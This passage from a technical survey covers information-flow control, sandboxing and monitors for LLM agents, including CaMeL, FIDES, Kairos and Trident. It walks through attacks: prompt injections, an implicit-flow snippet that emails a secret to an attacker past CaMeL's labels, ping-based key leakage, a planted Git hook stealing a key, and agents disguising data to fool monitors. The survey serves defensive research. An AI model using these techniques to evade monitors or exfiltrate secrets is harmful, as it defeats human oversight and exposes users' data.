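As in the seL4 proof, two runs that differ only in the cloud key must give the same public results. An agent fails this test if it posts the key, even in encoded form, or if it comments on an issue only when the key starts with a 7. The same formula covers integrity if ≈ means "agrees on everything trusted". An attacker's text may then change untrusted results but not, for example, which payments the agent makes. A language model's replies are partly random, so for an agent *P*(*s*) is a probability distribution over results.

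Noninterference compares two runs, while a monitor sees only one. Practical systems therefore attach labels to data and follow them through a single run.

### How labels combine

Denning proposed in 1976 that the labels should form a lattice, an ordered set in which any two labels have a lowest label above both (their join, written ⊔) and a highest label below both (their meet). In the simplest confidentiality lattice, public data may flow to secret places but not the reverse, and combining public with secret data gives the join, which is secret. Integrity works the other way round if trusted ranks above untrusted, because combining the two gives the meet, which is untrusted. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) puts untrusted at the top instead, so that a single join handles both kinds of label.

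A richer confidentiality label can list everyone allowed to read a piece of data, and the join of two such labels is the intersection of their lists. A richer integrity label can list everyone who may have written to the data, and the join is the union of the lists.

Joins only make labels more restrictive, so useful systems need exceptions. Declassification deliberately makes secret data less secret, as when a manager approves a summary for publication. Endorsement treats untrusted data as trusted, perhaps after a program has confirmed that a date taken from an email is valid. Each exception weakens the guarantee, so a reviewer has to know where exceptions occur and who can make them.

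### Uploading a build

Suppose a developer asks an agent to build a project and upload it to a public registry. Before the upload, the agent reads the developer's private signing key, a public web page about the build tool, and an email from a colleague.

| Data | Who may read it | Who may have influenced it |
|---|---|---|
| The request | Everyone | Developer |
| Private key | Developer | Developer |
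| Web page | Everyone | Anyone |
| Colleague's email | Developer, colleague | Colleague |
| Whatever the model writes next | Developer | Anyone |

The last row is the join of the others. Its readers are everyone ∩ {developer} ∩ everyone ∩ {developer, colleague} = {developer}, and the union of its possible writers is anyone. Public upload now breaks the rules against showing data to people outside its list of readers and against taking important actions on untrusted input. The agent cannot even tell the colleague that the build has finished. The monitor labels every output as if every input to the model had reached it, even though the finished program may contain nothing from the key, the page or the email.

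This label explosion reduces the number of tasks an agent can complete. Costa and colleagues measured the effect on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants prompt injections in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks. With no attack present, an ordinary agent running GPT-4o completed 75% of the office tasks and 93% of the Slack tasks. When a monitor enforced label rules on the same agent, these figures fell to 37% and 20%. The completion rate for travel tasks did not fall, because the rules let most travel tools run on untrusted data.

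The obvious remedy is to keep restricted data away from the model that decides what to do. For instance, a signing tool could use the key without showing it to the model. The signature would still depend on the key, so strict noninterference would forbid publishing it. The developer would have to declassify the signature, which is reasonable because signatures are designed not to reveal the key.

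### Planning before reading: CaMeL

CaMeL, a defence from Google DeepMind, has one model write the whole plan before anything untrusted arrives. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe its design and give a sample plan, which in simplified form looks like this:

```
messages = read_channel("general")
address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's address", messages)
send_message(address, "Meeting at 3pm")
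```

1. A planning model reads the user's request and writes the plan in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the plan and calls the tools. It keeps their results in variables that the planning model never sees.
3. A quarantined model, which has no tools, extracts the address from the messages.
4. The interpreter tags each value with its sources and permitted readers, and passes the tags on to anything computed from that value.
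5. Before each tool call, a policy function inspects the arguments and their tags, and allows or denies the call.

An attacker who posts in the channel cannot add a step that forwards the inbox, but can make the quarantined model return the wrong address, which the policy then has to handle. A rule against recipient addresses from untrusted sources would block the attack, but it would also block the legitimate task, because Bob's real address comes from the same channel.

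Software can also check a plan that exists in advance. CaMeLoT, an extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, turns the plan into a finite-state machine and checks it against rules about the whole run, such as "never isolate a computer from the network without approval". If some path breaks a rule, the planning model receives that path as a counterexample and tries to repair the plan. The checker treats every loop as one that may run any number of times, so it can reject a safe plan.

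### Hiding data from the planner: FIDES

FIDES, from Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, keeps the usual agent loop instead of fixing a plan in advance. It starts with a context labelled trusted and public. When a tool returns data that would raise the label, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass that name to another tool, and FIDES substitutes the contents, with their label, just before the call.

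A policy then checks the labels. An action with serious consequences must come from a trusted context, and each piece of data may go only to people on its list of readers. The policy can apply different rules to different arguments. For a message, FIDES might require that the decision to send it and the recipient both be trusted, but allow the text to draw on a web search. In the build example, the key, page and email would be stored in three variables, and the upload could proceed if the build used none of them.

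Sometimes the planner cannot choose the next step without knowing what a variable contains. Suppose the user wants a calendar entry if any recent email requests a meeting. An isolated model reads the emails and can answer only yes or no. FIDES shows the planner that answer, labeled as an untrusted Boolean. A policy can accept it because a single bit has little room for an injected instruction. If the answer is yes, the isolated model extracts the details into another variable, which the planner passes to the calendar without reading it.

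With its rules enforced, FIDES completed 59% of the office tasks and 48% of the Slack tasks, so hiding data recovered a good part of the performance lost to label explosion. Costa and colleagues found no real successful injection under these rules. However, they had labelled a field untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, and a company labelling its own data would not know in advance which fields attackers will use.

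### What the designers prove

CaMeL and FIDES provide weaker guarantees than noninterference. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes CaMeL's main property as control-flow integrity, meaning the agent makes only the tool calls laid out in a plan based on trusted information. Untrusted data can still determine which branch of the plan runs. The property holds if the user's request and the tool descriptions are trusted and the interpreter works correctly.

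CaMeL has no theorem showing that its data labels are sound, and Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found ways around them. One relies on a trick known since the 1970s:

```
tmp = True; rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(attacker, "rich")
```

CaMeL raises a variable's label only on a branch that runs. For example, a program might start with a public variable `rich` set to true and change it to false if a secret balance is low. If the balance is high, the program skips `rich = False`, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label. A variable marked public can therefore reveal secret information. CaMeL's retry loop also leaks information because it runs outside the label tracking. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit, so an attacker who can trigger many attempts can extract the secret bit by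 bit. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes part of the difficulty to Python, whose exceptions and dynamic typing make flows hard to analyse.

Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES satisfies explicit secrecy. This property requires that if two data stores contain the same public data, running the same sequence of steps on both leaves their public data the same. It therefore ignores anything an observer learns from which sequence the agent chose. For example, an agent could satisfy explicit secrecy but reveal the verdict of a confidential review by publicly closing either issue 12 or issue 13, depending on the verdict. The proof treats the model as deterministic and leaves out timing and other side channels. Costa and colleagues chose explicit secrecy over the stronger property of noninterference because noninterference would in practice forbid public actions after almost any access to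 a secret.

Garby and colleagues prove a form of noninterference for a small programming language in which agents can be written. A conversation with the model carries the join of the labels of everything sent to it, and the model's replies inherit that label. To avoid label explosion, a program can open a temporary copy of the conversation, read untrusted data there and then discard the copy.

Garby and colleagues' theorem allows for randomness and for runs that never finish. If two starting points look the same to an observer, and μ and ν give the probabilities of what the observer sees at the end of a run from each, then some ω with total probability at most 1 satisfies μ ≤ ω and ν ≤ ω for every outcome. If both runs always finish, then μ = ν, which is ordinary noninterference. Otherwise, the statistical distance between μ and ν is at most the average of the two runs' chances of not finishing.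 Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean, and the program they verified is the one that calls the model. A second theorem shows that endorsing untrusted data cannot expose secrets. Developers still have to label every source correctly and put a check in front of every sensitive tool.

A security guarantee that holds for one agent can fail in a system of several. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which a coordinating agent asked one agent to query a database and another to send the summary to Julie on Slack. All three used CaMeL. An instruction planted in the database passed through the first two agents as untrusted data, but the coordinator then put the summary in its request to the third agent, which treated the whole request as trusted. As a result, the third agent's plan included an email to an outsider. The researchers fixed this by sending instructions and data between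 agents separately. On their benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with the fix, so the benchmark's attacks rarely exploited the flaw.

### Checking where a tool call came from

Two systems from 2026 let the model read untrusted text while planning, and they check each tool call just before it runs. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) explains why earlier checks can fail. For example, an add-on's code might always send an email, while its written description tells the model what to put in it. The code can be identical whether the description is harmless or asks for a password, so a reviewer who studies only the code cannot tell the two cases apart.

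PACE freezes the proposed call and compares its arguments with values the agent has already handled. It builds a graph of how data may have travelled and looks for paths from secrets or attacker-controlled text to an unsafe effect. If it finds such a path, it computes the lowest-weight set of links to cut, which often means blocking the call. A separate check determines whether the user's authenticated request authorizes each effect, such as writing to a particular file.

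Li and colleagues prove that a harmful chain cannot finish if the graph represents every link in it and the cut takes effect in time. They state that this falls short of noninterference. The graph can miss secrets that the model paraphrases, translates or splits up, and effects that a tool does not declare. The version they tested is also weaker than the one the proof covers, because it can restore a blocked call when the authorization check approves it.

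The tests show why they allowed this. In a comparison of PACE's parts, attacks on AgentDojo tasks succeeded 37.4% of the time with no defence. Path checking alone stopped them all but cut task completion from 76.8% to 13.6%. The authorization check alone also stopped them all, and the agent still completed 64.6% of tasks. This result counts against the view that data flow needs its own controls. The authorization check may have done well partly because most benchmark attacks, unlike the release plan attack, demand something the user never requested, which the check can catch.

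Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, applies a finer test to each part of a call. (He also designed Portico, the monitor that revokes rights during a task.) A log from a failed test may legitimately tell a coding agent which file to open. The same log should not choose the tool, mark a change as approved or trigger a second attempt. The system therefore requires three kinds of authority before a call can run:

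- Each protected field, such as the recipient or approval status, needs a trusted source or a "typed release", a narrow endorsement that a validator issues for that field alone.
- A payload that changes something, such as a code patch, needs authorization for its exact effect on the current state of the repository.
- The call itself needs a single-use permission, which prevents untrusted text from causing extra calls or retries.

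All three refer to one record of the proposed action, so changing any detail afterwards invalidates the permission. A file path from the log could be accepted as a file path but rejected as a command. Text copied into a comment stays untrusted if another agent reads it later.

Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorized actions in 400 coding episodes, 231 of which completed their tasks safely. The other 169 included 73 with malformed outputs and 61 in which an action never received authorization for its effects. The guarantee depends on correct policies and validators, which take work to write. An audit of policies covering 24 kinds of action and 149 fields initially found 18 problems, including approvals granted in ordinary prose. When another company hosts the model, the system can control what goes into the prompt for a protected field but cannot verify what happens inside the model.

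### Checking the agent's code

Another approach puts the restrictions into the programming language. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026) built *LACUNA* on the language Scala. A LACUNA program contains calls such as `agent[Report]("summarize these findings")`. When the program reaches this call, a model writes code that should produce a report. The compiler checks the code against its surroundings before any of it runs, and returns errors to the model so that it can try again.

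The types also record capabilities. Code can use the network only if the surrounding program has given it a network capability, and it cannot keep a capability outside the block that granted it. Secret data sits in a container called `Classified`. A program may apply a function to the contents only if the function holds no capabilities, and the result goes back into a container. For example, the function can search a contract for risky clauses but cannot print or send the contract. The container comes from an earlier system, TACIT. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) contrasts TACIT, which checks code before it runs, with CaMeL, which tracks data while the code runs.

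With TACIT, a model had to write the function before seeing the contract. LACUNA lets the function call a second, trusted model that runs on the user's machine. This second model reads the contract and writes further code under the same restrictions. The hosted model that planned the work never sees the contract.

The compiler cannot check whether code does what the user wanted, and Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker can still misuse a capability the task needs. In their tests, 7 of 949 AgentDojo attacks succeeded with Gemini 2.5 Pro and 1 of 949 with o4-mini. The protection also requires Scala's safe mode, because without it code could start an outside program that the compiler never checks.

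### Following influence through a model

Critics object that nobody can track a label precisely through a language model. The output of an ordinary program that adds two numbers clearly depends on both, but a model's reply may depend on only one sentence in its context. Labelling the reply with the join of all the inputs' labels is safe but often useless, while matching text, as PACE does, misses paraphrases.

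Most of the designs above control what the model reads, so they do not have to work out what it used. This works well when the task allows it. Costa and colleagues also mention research on more permissive labels, in which the system identifies the messages that influenced a reply and then regenerates the reply from those messages alone. The new reply depends on fewer inputs, though an attacker's text might still affect which messages the system keeps.

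### Tasks that depend on what the agent finds

A plan written in advance can also work poorly for open-ended tasks. Costa and colleagues call a task data independent if the same sequence of tool calls and the same final response would solve it whatever the data is. By their count, 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks and about 44% of its banking tasks are not data independent. Bug fixes usually aren't either, because the bug report and test results determine which files the agent has to change.

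Yes-or-no questions in FIDES and nested model calls in LACUNA let an agent adapt without showing untrusted text to the planner. They work best when someone can foresee the possible answers. A coding agent that gets an unfamiliar error message often needs to read the message itself, which makes the context untrusted. The developer then has to endorse something or give up on the task. When Garby and colleagues removed endorsement from their agent, the share of banking tasks it completed fell from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from about 65% to 54% with another.

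### Bias without an instruction

Untrusted data can also mislead an agent without containing instructions, as with the product review and the wrong coffee maker. A false test result can make an agent take the wrong branch of its plan. CaMeL's plan stays intact in both cases, because the plan was written to use the data to choose between branches.

Labels can catch this if the policy requires every argument and every decision to be trusted, but such an agent could not choose a product from reviews. A less strict approach limits how much the attacker can influence. In an example from Garby and colleagues, a quarantined model sorts an email into one of *n* fixed categories, and the program endorses the category. The sender can influence at most log₂ *n* bits of the reply. This keeps arbitrary text out of the reply but does not limit the damage, because one bit is enough to approve a payment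 or release a faulty build.

Garby and colleagues ran into this limit in their tests on AgentDojo's banking tasks, where 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both cases, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Blocking every payment based on a file would have stopped both the theft and the legitimate task. The real bill and the forged one carry the same label, so no rule based on labels can distinguish them.

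## What a formal security model for an agent sandbox would have to state

As the forged bill shows, a designer can prove that no payment leaves without the monitor's approval, whatever the agent does, but cannot prove that the monitor approves only the right payments. Under the fourth view, confinement and authorization are therefore separate properties, each with its own adversary and kind of evidence. A designer can then prove confinement under stated assumptions and measure how well authorization works.

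*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by Christodorescu and colleagues, divides the problem in much the same way. They treat the model as untrusted and want the surrounding system to block prohibited actions whatever their cause, so an attempt that the monitor stops does not count as a security violation. They add that enforcing a policy does not show that it captures what the user wanted, and they call verifying that it does an open research problem.

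### Ten things to specify

For an agent that fixes a bug and publishes the result, a complete model would have to cover:

- Principals, the people on whose authority the agent acts. If a project's settings file can change the policy, whoever wrote the project is in effect a principal too.
- Protected assets. Protecting the developer's laptop does not protect the people who will install the published software.
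- The adversary. A defence against hostile text may fail against a hostile agent, and a defence against one hostile agent may fail against several that cooperate.
- Channels, meaning every route by which the agent can affect or inform the outside. Claude Code once allowed the network command `ping` without approval, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes how injected text could use it to leak an API key through the address lookup that `ping` performs.
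- The trusted base. A bug in any trusted component can break the guarantee, so users need to know what they are relying on.
- The property, stated over traces, which are sequences of events. Without a definite test to apply to traces, nobody can prove the claim or find a counterexample.
- The source of the policy. An attacker who can influence the policy has no need to defeat the monitor that enforces it.
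- Behaviour over time and across sessions. In one real attack, a document or website planted instructions in ChatGPT's long-term memory, and the app then leaked the user's later conversations.
- Composition with other services. A code host may run a build whenever someone pushes a change, so one permitted push can set off actions outside the sandbox's control.
- Evidence that the deployed system matches the model. A theorem about a design protects nobody if the installed program behaves differently.

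*AI Sandboxes* (2026) offers a shorter template for recording a single threat. Its six parts are the actor, the path of the attack, the boundary it violates, the component it targets, its impact, and the control that should stop it, with the evidence for that control and the remaining risk. The template would suit an incident report, but a set of these records covers only the threats that somebody has thought of.

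How much a guarantee protects can depend on which adversary the model assumes. *Bounded Agents* (2026), a proposal for agents that delegate work to one another, uses a monitor that forbids certain pairs of actions within a session. It assumes that the adversary cannot operate across sessions. Suppose the monitor forbids reading a secret and posting in public in the same session. An agent could still save the secret to a file in one session and post it in the next without breaking the rule.

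### Events and guarantees in Kairos

Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026), in *KAIROS*, give the fullest example of a model that keeps the two properties apart. Kairos runs an unmodified coding agent in a microVM, with a monitor on the host. The monitor does not see the agent's tool calls. It sees only what crosses the boundary, as a series of events:

*e* = (*ch*, *dir*, *op*, *obj*, *v*)

Here *ch* is the channel (file, network or control), *dir* is the direction (in or out), *op* is the operation, *obj* is the path, destination or person at the other end, and *v* is the content. The user gives the task and gets the answer through the control channel. Tool calls, shell commands and scripts that the agent wrote all produce the same kinds of event, so the agent cannot get around a rule by opening a file through the shell instead of the file-reading tool.

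The trace σ = *e*₁*e*₂…*e*ₙ lists the events in the order in which the monitor sees them. An effect is an outgoing event that becomes visible outside once the monitor releases it. A second sequence, obs(σ), contains only the released effects, in order of release. For each effect *e*ᵢ, the monitor looks at the trace so far and makes one of three decisions:

δ(σᵢ₋₁, *e*ᵢ) ∈ {release, refuse, defer}

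The monitor can refuse an effect, which permanently suppresses it and informs the agent, or defer it, which holds the effect while the agent continues. Kairos applies a deferred file change to a copy that only the agent can see. It can hold a network request at a proxy and give the agent a stand-in reply if the agent only needs confirmation that the request succeeded. If the agent needs the real reply, such as the contents of a web page, the decision must be made before the request is sent.

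Hempel and colleagues state three confinement guarantees:

1. Every effect that leaves the sandbox passes the monitor.
2. No effect becomes irreversible before the monitor releases it.
3. An effect that the monitor refuses never becomes observable outside.

These guarantees follow almost directly from the definitions, since an effect enters obs(σ) only when the monitor releases it. They hold even if the agent is completely hostile, and regardless of how the monitor decides. But they depend on three assumptions that are hard to satisfy.

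The first assumption is that the agent has no other channels to the outside. The second is that the company that hosts the model does not collude with the attacker. The agent has to send that company its context, so Kairos treats the connection as internal and lets the traffic through. An attacker with an account at the same company could also be a problem if the service offered a way to pass data between accounts. Running the model inside the sandbox would remove the second assumption.

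The third is that the trusted base, which consists of the host, the isolation layer and the monitor, works correctly. Hempel and colleagues apply Anderson's requirement that this base be small enough to validate, but they assume that theirs is and do not demonstrate it. Their prototype relies on Cloud Hypervisor, several layers of file-system software, and a proxy that decrypts web traffic, which is much more software than seL4's verified kernel.

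### Why authorization is only a goal

Authorization in Kairos comes without a guarantee. The goal is that the monitor releases no effect that an untrusted value steers, and sends no data to a recipient without clearance for it. An operator writes a policy that lists the trusted sources, the sensitive data and the clearance of each outside party. The monitor then applies it as follows:

- Refuse the effect if an explicit rule forbids it.
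- Release it if every value that steers it comes from a trusted source and ℓ(*e*) ⊑ clr(*obj*), where ℓ(*e*) is the sensitivity of the data it carries and clr(*obj*) is the clearance of its destination.
- Defer it otherwise.

The steering values include the recipient of a message and the command a script will run. The body of a message can be untrusted, as in FIDES.

The monitor cannot observe how the agent turned what it read into what it sends, so it compares text at the boundary. It treats a value as trusted if it matches one from a trusted source, ignoring case and spaces, and treats data as sensitive if it contains a known piece of sensitive text. The monitor defers a harmless effect when it fails to recognize a trusted value, but it may release a secret that it fails to recognize. Suppose the user names a public issue tracker in the task, and the agent posts the cloud key there in an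 encoded form. The policy releases the post without further review because the destination is trusted and the encoded key matches no known sensitive text.

For this reason, Hempel and colleagues assume a weaker adversary for authorization, an agent that follows injected instructions completely but does not deliberately disguise data. If the agent does disguise data, only the confinement guarantees hold. The alternative is to label every effect with everything the agent has read, but that would bring back label explosion, and the monitor would defer nearly everything after the agent read its first untrusted page.

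Authorization also depends on what the user wants, which nobody can fully write down. A decision oracle therefore judges whether to allow each deferred effect. The oracle is a second language model by default, but it could be a person. It receives the task, the policy, the trace and the untrusted text behind each effect, so an attacker can use that text to try to influence its decision.

Hempel and colleagues leave the oracle out of the trusted base for confinement because the three guarantees hold whatever it answers. The oracle rules on deferred effects alone, so it has no power to reverse the policy's own refusals, and the monitor treats an unreadable answer as a refusal. If the oracle refused everything, the monitor would release only what the policy itself allows. The authorization goal does depend on the oracle's judgment, so Hempel and colleagues measure authorization instead of proving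 it. On AgentDojo, attack success fell from 47.0% to 2.7%.

### What a monitor can enforce

The option to defer matters because of a result from 2000. Fred Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies*, studied monitors that watch a program and can only stop it. Such a monitor sees one run, up to the present moment. Write good(σ) for the test that the monitor applies to a run σ. Schneider showed that the policy must then meet three conditions:

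- A system satisfies the policy exactly when good(σ) holds for every run σ that the system can produce.
- If good(τ) fails for a finite run τ, it fails for every run that begins with τ.
- If good(σ) fails, it already fails for some finite beginning of σ.

The second condition holds because the program might stop at any point, so the monitor cannot allow something bad and rely on a later step to correct it. Policies that meet all three conditions are safety properties, which rule out some definite bad event. Access control qualifies because a forbidden access is bad the moment it happens. Information flow fails the first condition because, like noninterference, it depends on comparing runs.

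A monitor can still prevent leaks by enforcing a stricter rule. Schneider's example forbids sending any message after reading any file. The monitor tracks only two states, "no file read" and "file read", and stops the program if it tries to send in the second. A coding agent under this rule could read the source code but never publish the fix. The rule also works only if the definition of "send" covers every way to send data, and the `ping` case shows how easily a designer can miss one.

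Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (2005), modelled a stronger monitor called an edit automaton. It can suppress an action, report to the program that it succeeded, and perform it later. They require that the monitor's output always obey the policy and that it leave valid runs unchanged.

A policy might let an untrusted script stay in a repository only if a reviewer approves it. The run "write script" breaks this policy, but the longer run "write script, approve" satisfies it, so the policy is not a safety property. A monitor that can only stop the program would have to stop it at the first step, so the script could never be approved. An edit automaton can hold the write until the reviewer approves it, much as a database holds a transaction's changes until the transaction is complete.

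If every run eventually ends, as an agent's task does when the harness sets a step limit, an edit automaton can in principle enforce any policy that judges runs one at a time. This requires that software can decide whether a given run is valid, and that doing nothing counts as valid. For runs that can go on forever, Ligatti and colleagues prove that edit automata can enforce all the safety properties that simpler monitors can, and some other properties. They still cannot enforce some useful policies. With two or more resources, for example, an edit automaton cannot enforce the rule that a program must eventually close whatever it opens, because the program can always open a new resource before closing the previous one.

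Neither kind of monitor can enforce policies that compare different runs, such as noninterference, so holding actions does not help with those. Ligatti and colleagues also point out that a monitor cannot hold back an email and still get the real reply to it. Kairos has the same limit when the agent needs a web page, so deferral helps more with files than with network requests. The theorem also requires a correct test of which runs are valid. No such test exists for whether a script is what the user wanted, so the oracle's answer is a guess.

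### The planted hook

Hempel and colleagues illustrate deferral with a pre-commit hook, which Git runs whenever somebody records a change. Alice asks an agent to set up a project using a guide. Eve wrote the guide and included an instruction to install a hook that steals Alice's key.

The table below shows this as a trace, with some details added. Suppose the operator's policy allows requests with public data to the guide's website and approves commits to the project. It also has an explicit rule against sending Alice's key anywhere. The key is in a file in the project folder, which the policy marks as sensitive.

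| Event | Channel and direction | What crosses the boundary | Policy's decision | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| *e*₁ | Control, in | Alice's task, with the guide's address | None needed | The address becomes a trusted value |
| *e*₂ | Network, out | Request for the guide | Release | The request goes out |
| *e*₃ | Network, in | Eve's text | None needed | The text counts as untrusted |
| *e*₄ | File, out | The hook, which contains Eve's command | Defer | The hook exists only in the agent's copy of the project |
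| *e*₅ | File, in | Alice's key, which the hook reads when the agent commits | None needed | The monitor records the key as sensitive |
| *e*₆ | Network, out | The key, addressed to Eve's server | Refuse | The key never leaves |
| *e*₇ | File, out | The new commit | Release | The monitor holds the commit, because it builds on the copy with the hook |
| *e*₈ | File, out | The same commit, which the agent makes again | Release | The commit reaches Alice's project |

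Between *e*₇ and *e*₈, the oracle reviews the hook and refuses it because it tried to send Alice's key to Eve. The monitor discards the copy, including the first commit, and tells the agent that the hook was not installed. The final observable sequence is obs(σ) = *e*₂*e*₈, which omits the agent's reply to Alice because Kairos never holds that reply.

A monitor that could not defer would have had to decide at *e*₄. If it had released the hook, the refusal at *e*₆ would still have protected the key that time, but the hook would have stayed in the project and run the next time Alice committed from a terminal outside the sandbox. If it had refused the hook, it would also have had to refuse the many legitimate hooks that check formatting or run tests.

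The example works because the hook produces evidence of its purpose while the monitor is still holding it. A hook that did nothing until a certain date would produce no such evidence, so the oracle would have to judge it from its text alone. An attacker might also be able to force an early decision. The prototype can keep only one group of held effects open at a time, so a second effect that needs holding makes the oracle rule on the first group immediately. Eve could try to use her guide to trigger such an effect before the agent commits. Kairos also cannot erase Eve's text from the agent's context, so the agent may try to install the hook again.

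### Agents that can only propose changes

*Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (Sterling, 2026) describes a different approach to confinement, in a design called Agentic Redux. Several agents share one official record of the state of their work. Each agent sees only its own part of that state and can only propose changes. An ordinary program, called the meta-agent despite not being an agent, takes one proposal at a time, works out the state it would produce, and checks that state against invariants, which are conditions that must always hold. It then approves the change, rejects it or escalates it to a person.

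In Sterling's example, two agents share a budget of $100,000. One wants to spend $45,000 and the other $60,000. Each purchase fits the budget by itself, and an agent that saw only its own records might approve it. The meta-agent approves whichever proposal it considers first and rejects the other, because the total would exceed the budget.

Sterling's agent-confinement proposition has two parts. Let *s*₁ and *s*₂ be two states, let project(*s*, *r*) be the slice of state *s* visible to an agent in role *r*, and let ω be the list of answers that the agent gets from language models and tools. If project(*s*₁, *r*) = project(*s*₂, *r*), then the agent α makes the same proposal in both states:

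α(project(*s*₁, *r*), ω) = α(project(*s*₂, *r*), ω)

If the cloud key is outside a testing agent's slice, the agent proposes the same thing whatever the key is. This amounts to noninterference for a single step. The second part is that asking an agent for a proposal leaves the official state unchanged. A separate theorem shows that if the first state satisfies all the invariants, so does every later one. Like Bell and LaPadula's, the proof is by induction, and each step holds because an approved change has already passed the check.

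The first part follows directly from Sterling's definition of an agent as a function of its slice and ω. The definition also requires that nothing else the agent receives depend on the official state. A tool that returned the contents of a file outside the slice would violate this requirement, and on a strict reading so would a conversation history containing an older version of the slice. Something has to enforce these conditions on a real agent with a shell, but Sterling leaves the sandbox and the harness out of scope and assumes that they work. The proposition therefore describes what follows once confinement is in place, while Kairos describes a mechanism for achieving it.

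Each invariant checks only the proposed new state, a problem familiar from System Z. A rule such as "nobody may lower a document's classification" concerns the change between two states, so the designer would have to store the old classification as part of the state and compare it with the new one.

### How complete the two models are

| Item | Kairos | Agentic Redux |
|---|---|---|
| Principals | Stated: the user who sets the task and the operator who writes the policy | Partly stated: a role for each agent and for a human reviewer |
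| Protected assets | Stated: the shared folder, declared sensitive data and outside parties | Stated: the official state and the integrity of its log, but not the log's secrecy |
| Adversary | Stated separately for each property | Stated: agents may propose anything, and the code for a particular field of work may have bugs |
| Channels | Stated: file, network and control | Assumed: agents can act only through proposals |
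| Trusted base | Stated: host, isolation layer and monitor | Partly stated: the checking program, plus a sandbox and harness that Sterling assumes to work |
| Property over traces | Guaranteed for confinement; a goal for authorization | Guaranteed: every reachable state satisfies the invariants, and the log records every decision |
| Source of the policy | Stated: the operator, with an oracle for deferred cases | Stated: an expert's description of the field, from which a language model can derive the invariants |
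| Time and sessions | Partly covered: labels stay with files, but data can lose its label if the agent moves it before reading it | Partly covered: runs of any length, but no private memory for agents |
| Composition | Mostly missing: everything inside one sandbox counts as one agent | Covered for agents that share the official state; the harness must record outside events correctly |
| Evidence of a match | Partly covered: a working prototype and tests | Partly covered: written proofs and working code |

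Kairos states more about the boundary, and Agentic Redux more about what several agents may do together. The weakest part of both is the evidence that the deployed system matches the model. Hempel and colleagues ran their attack tests on benchmarks with simulated tools, using an adapter that turned each tool call into events, so the tests exercised the policy and the oracle but not the virtual machine. Sterling reports that a language model wrote about 90% of the appendix containing the proofs, and reports correcting errors in earlier versions. Readers have to check these proofs by hand.

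Hempel and colleagues exclude four kinds of harm. The first is escape from the isolation layer, which would defeat all three guarantees. The second is covert channels, so an agent could signal to an accomplice through the timing of permitted requests. The third is loss of availability, as when an agent stalls the work or uses up the machine's resources. The fourth is harm from the text of the agent's reply. If the agent tells Alice to paste a command into her own terminal and she does, the command runs outside the sandbox without passing through the monitor.

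*Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) addresses the first of these. It assumes that the agent has already escaped its sandbox and controls the kernel of its virtual machine, and that the host may be helping the agent. It puts the agent and its supervisor in two virtual machines that the processor protects from each other and from the host. The agent's machine has no network connection or disk that it can use by itself. Every file and network request goes to the supervisor's machine, which checks the policy, holds the credentials and keeps the log.

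Abdollahi and colleagues thus replace the host in the trusted base with the processor's security features and their firmware. This cut network connection throughput by 51–70% in their prototype. They reduce the opportunities for covert channels but do not claim to close them, and they treat misuse of services that the agent is allowed to contact as out of scope.

### Proving part of authorization

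*Trident* (2026) shows that designers don't have to rely on measurement alone for authorization. Like CaMeL, it has one language model that plans without reading untrusted text and another that reads the text but has no permissions. A third model writes the policy, and it receives only the user's request, an administrator's general policy and the tool descriptions. It doesn't receive the planner's requests, because an attacker's text might have influenced them. A monitor checks the output of all three models, and none of the models is part of the trusted base.

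As in FIDES, the planner can query untrusted data using questions with a fixed set of answers, but here the monitor counts each answer against a budget. A yes-or-no answer uses one bit. A second budget covers feedback that an attacker can trigger, such as a failed query or a blocked call. If the budgets are *b* and *f* bits, and the trusted inputs and randomness stay the same, an attacker can select among at most 2 to the power *b* + *f* observable traces. Budgets of six and four bits allow at most 1,024 traces. The proofs of this bound and of the guarantee that every executed call satisfies the administrator's policy are machine-checked in Lean.

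Checking the bound means comparing many possible runs, and Schneider's result seems to imply that a monitor cannot enforce such a property. The monitor avoids this problem by enforcing a stricter rule on each run, namely that the planner never receives more bits than the budget allows. Like the limit on endorsed categories in Garby and colleagues' example, the bound does not limit the damage, so the administrator's policy still has to rule out unacceptable outcomes. *Trident* also requires developers to rebuild the agent around three models, while Kairos works with an agent whose code nobody can inspect.

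### Policies that change and programs that differ from their models

Kairos and Agentic Redux both assume the policy is set before the work starts, but organizations revise their policies. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) shows how a small revision can go wrong. Suppose a monitor searches a list of permissions in order. The first entry permits one deletion of file B, and the second permits one deletion of file A. The agent can delete A and then B.

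Suppose somebody widens the first permission to cover either file. When the agent deletes A, the monitor uses up that permission, leaving none for B, but the agent can still delete A a second time. The wider policy therefore blocks legitimate work and allows a forbidden action. For this reason, Shivakumar and colleagues treat safety and the preservation of legitimate work as separate properties. A model must specify how the agent uses up permissions before anyone can check either property.

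*Agenra* also goes further than most in connecting its theorem to the running program. The code that checks each live call is itself a set of Lean functions with proofs, which brings it closer to seL4, whose proofs cover the kernel's C code. *PerMIT* (2026), which protects agents' long-term memory, is more typical. Lean checks its theorems, but the match between the Lean model and the paper's rules rests on a written argument.

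Abdollahi and colleagues use attestation as another kind of evidence. The processor's firmware measures each virtual machine's initial software and settings, and a user can remotely compare the result with the expected value. A match confirms that the intended supervisor started, but it does not rule out bugs or a later takeover.

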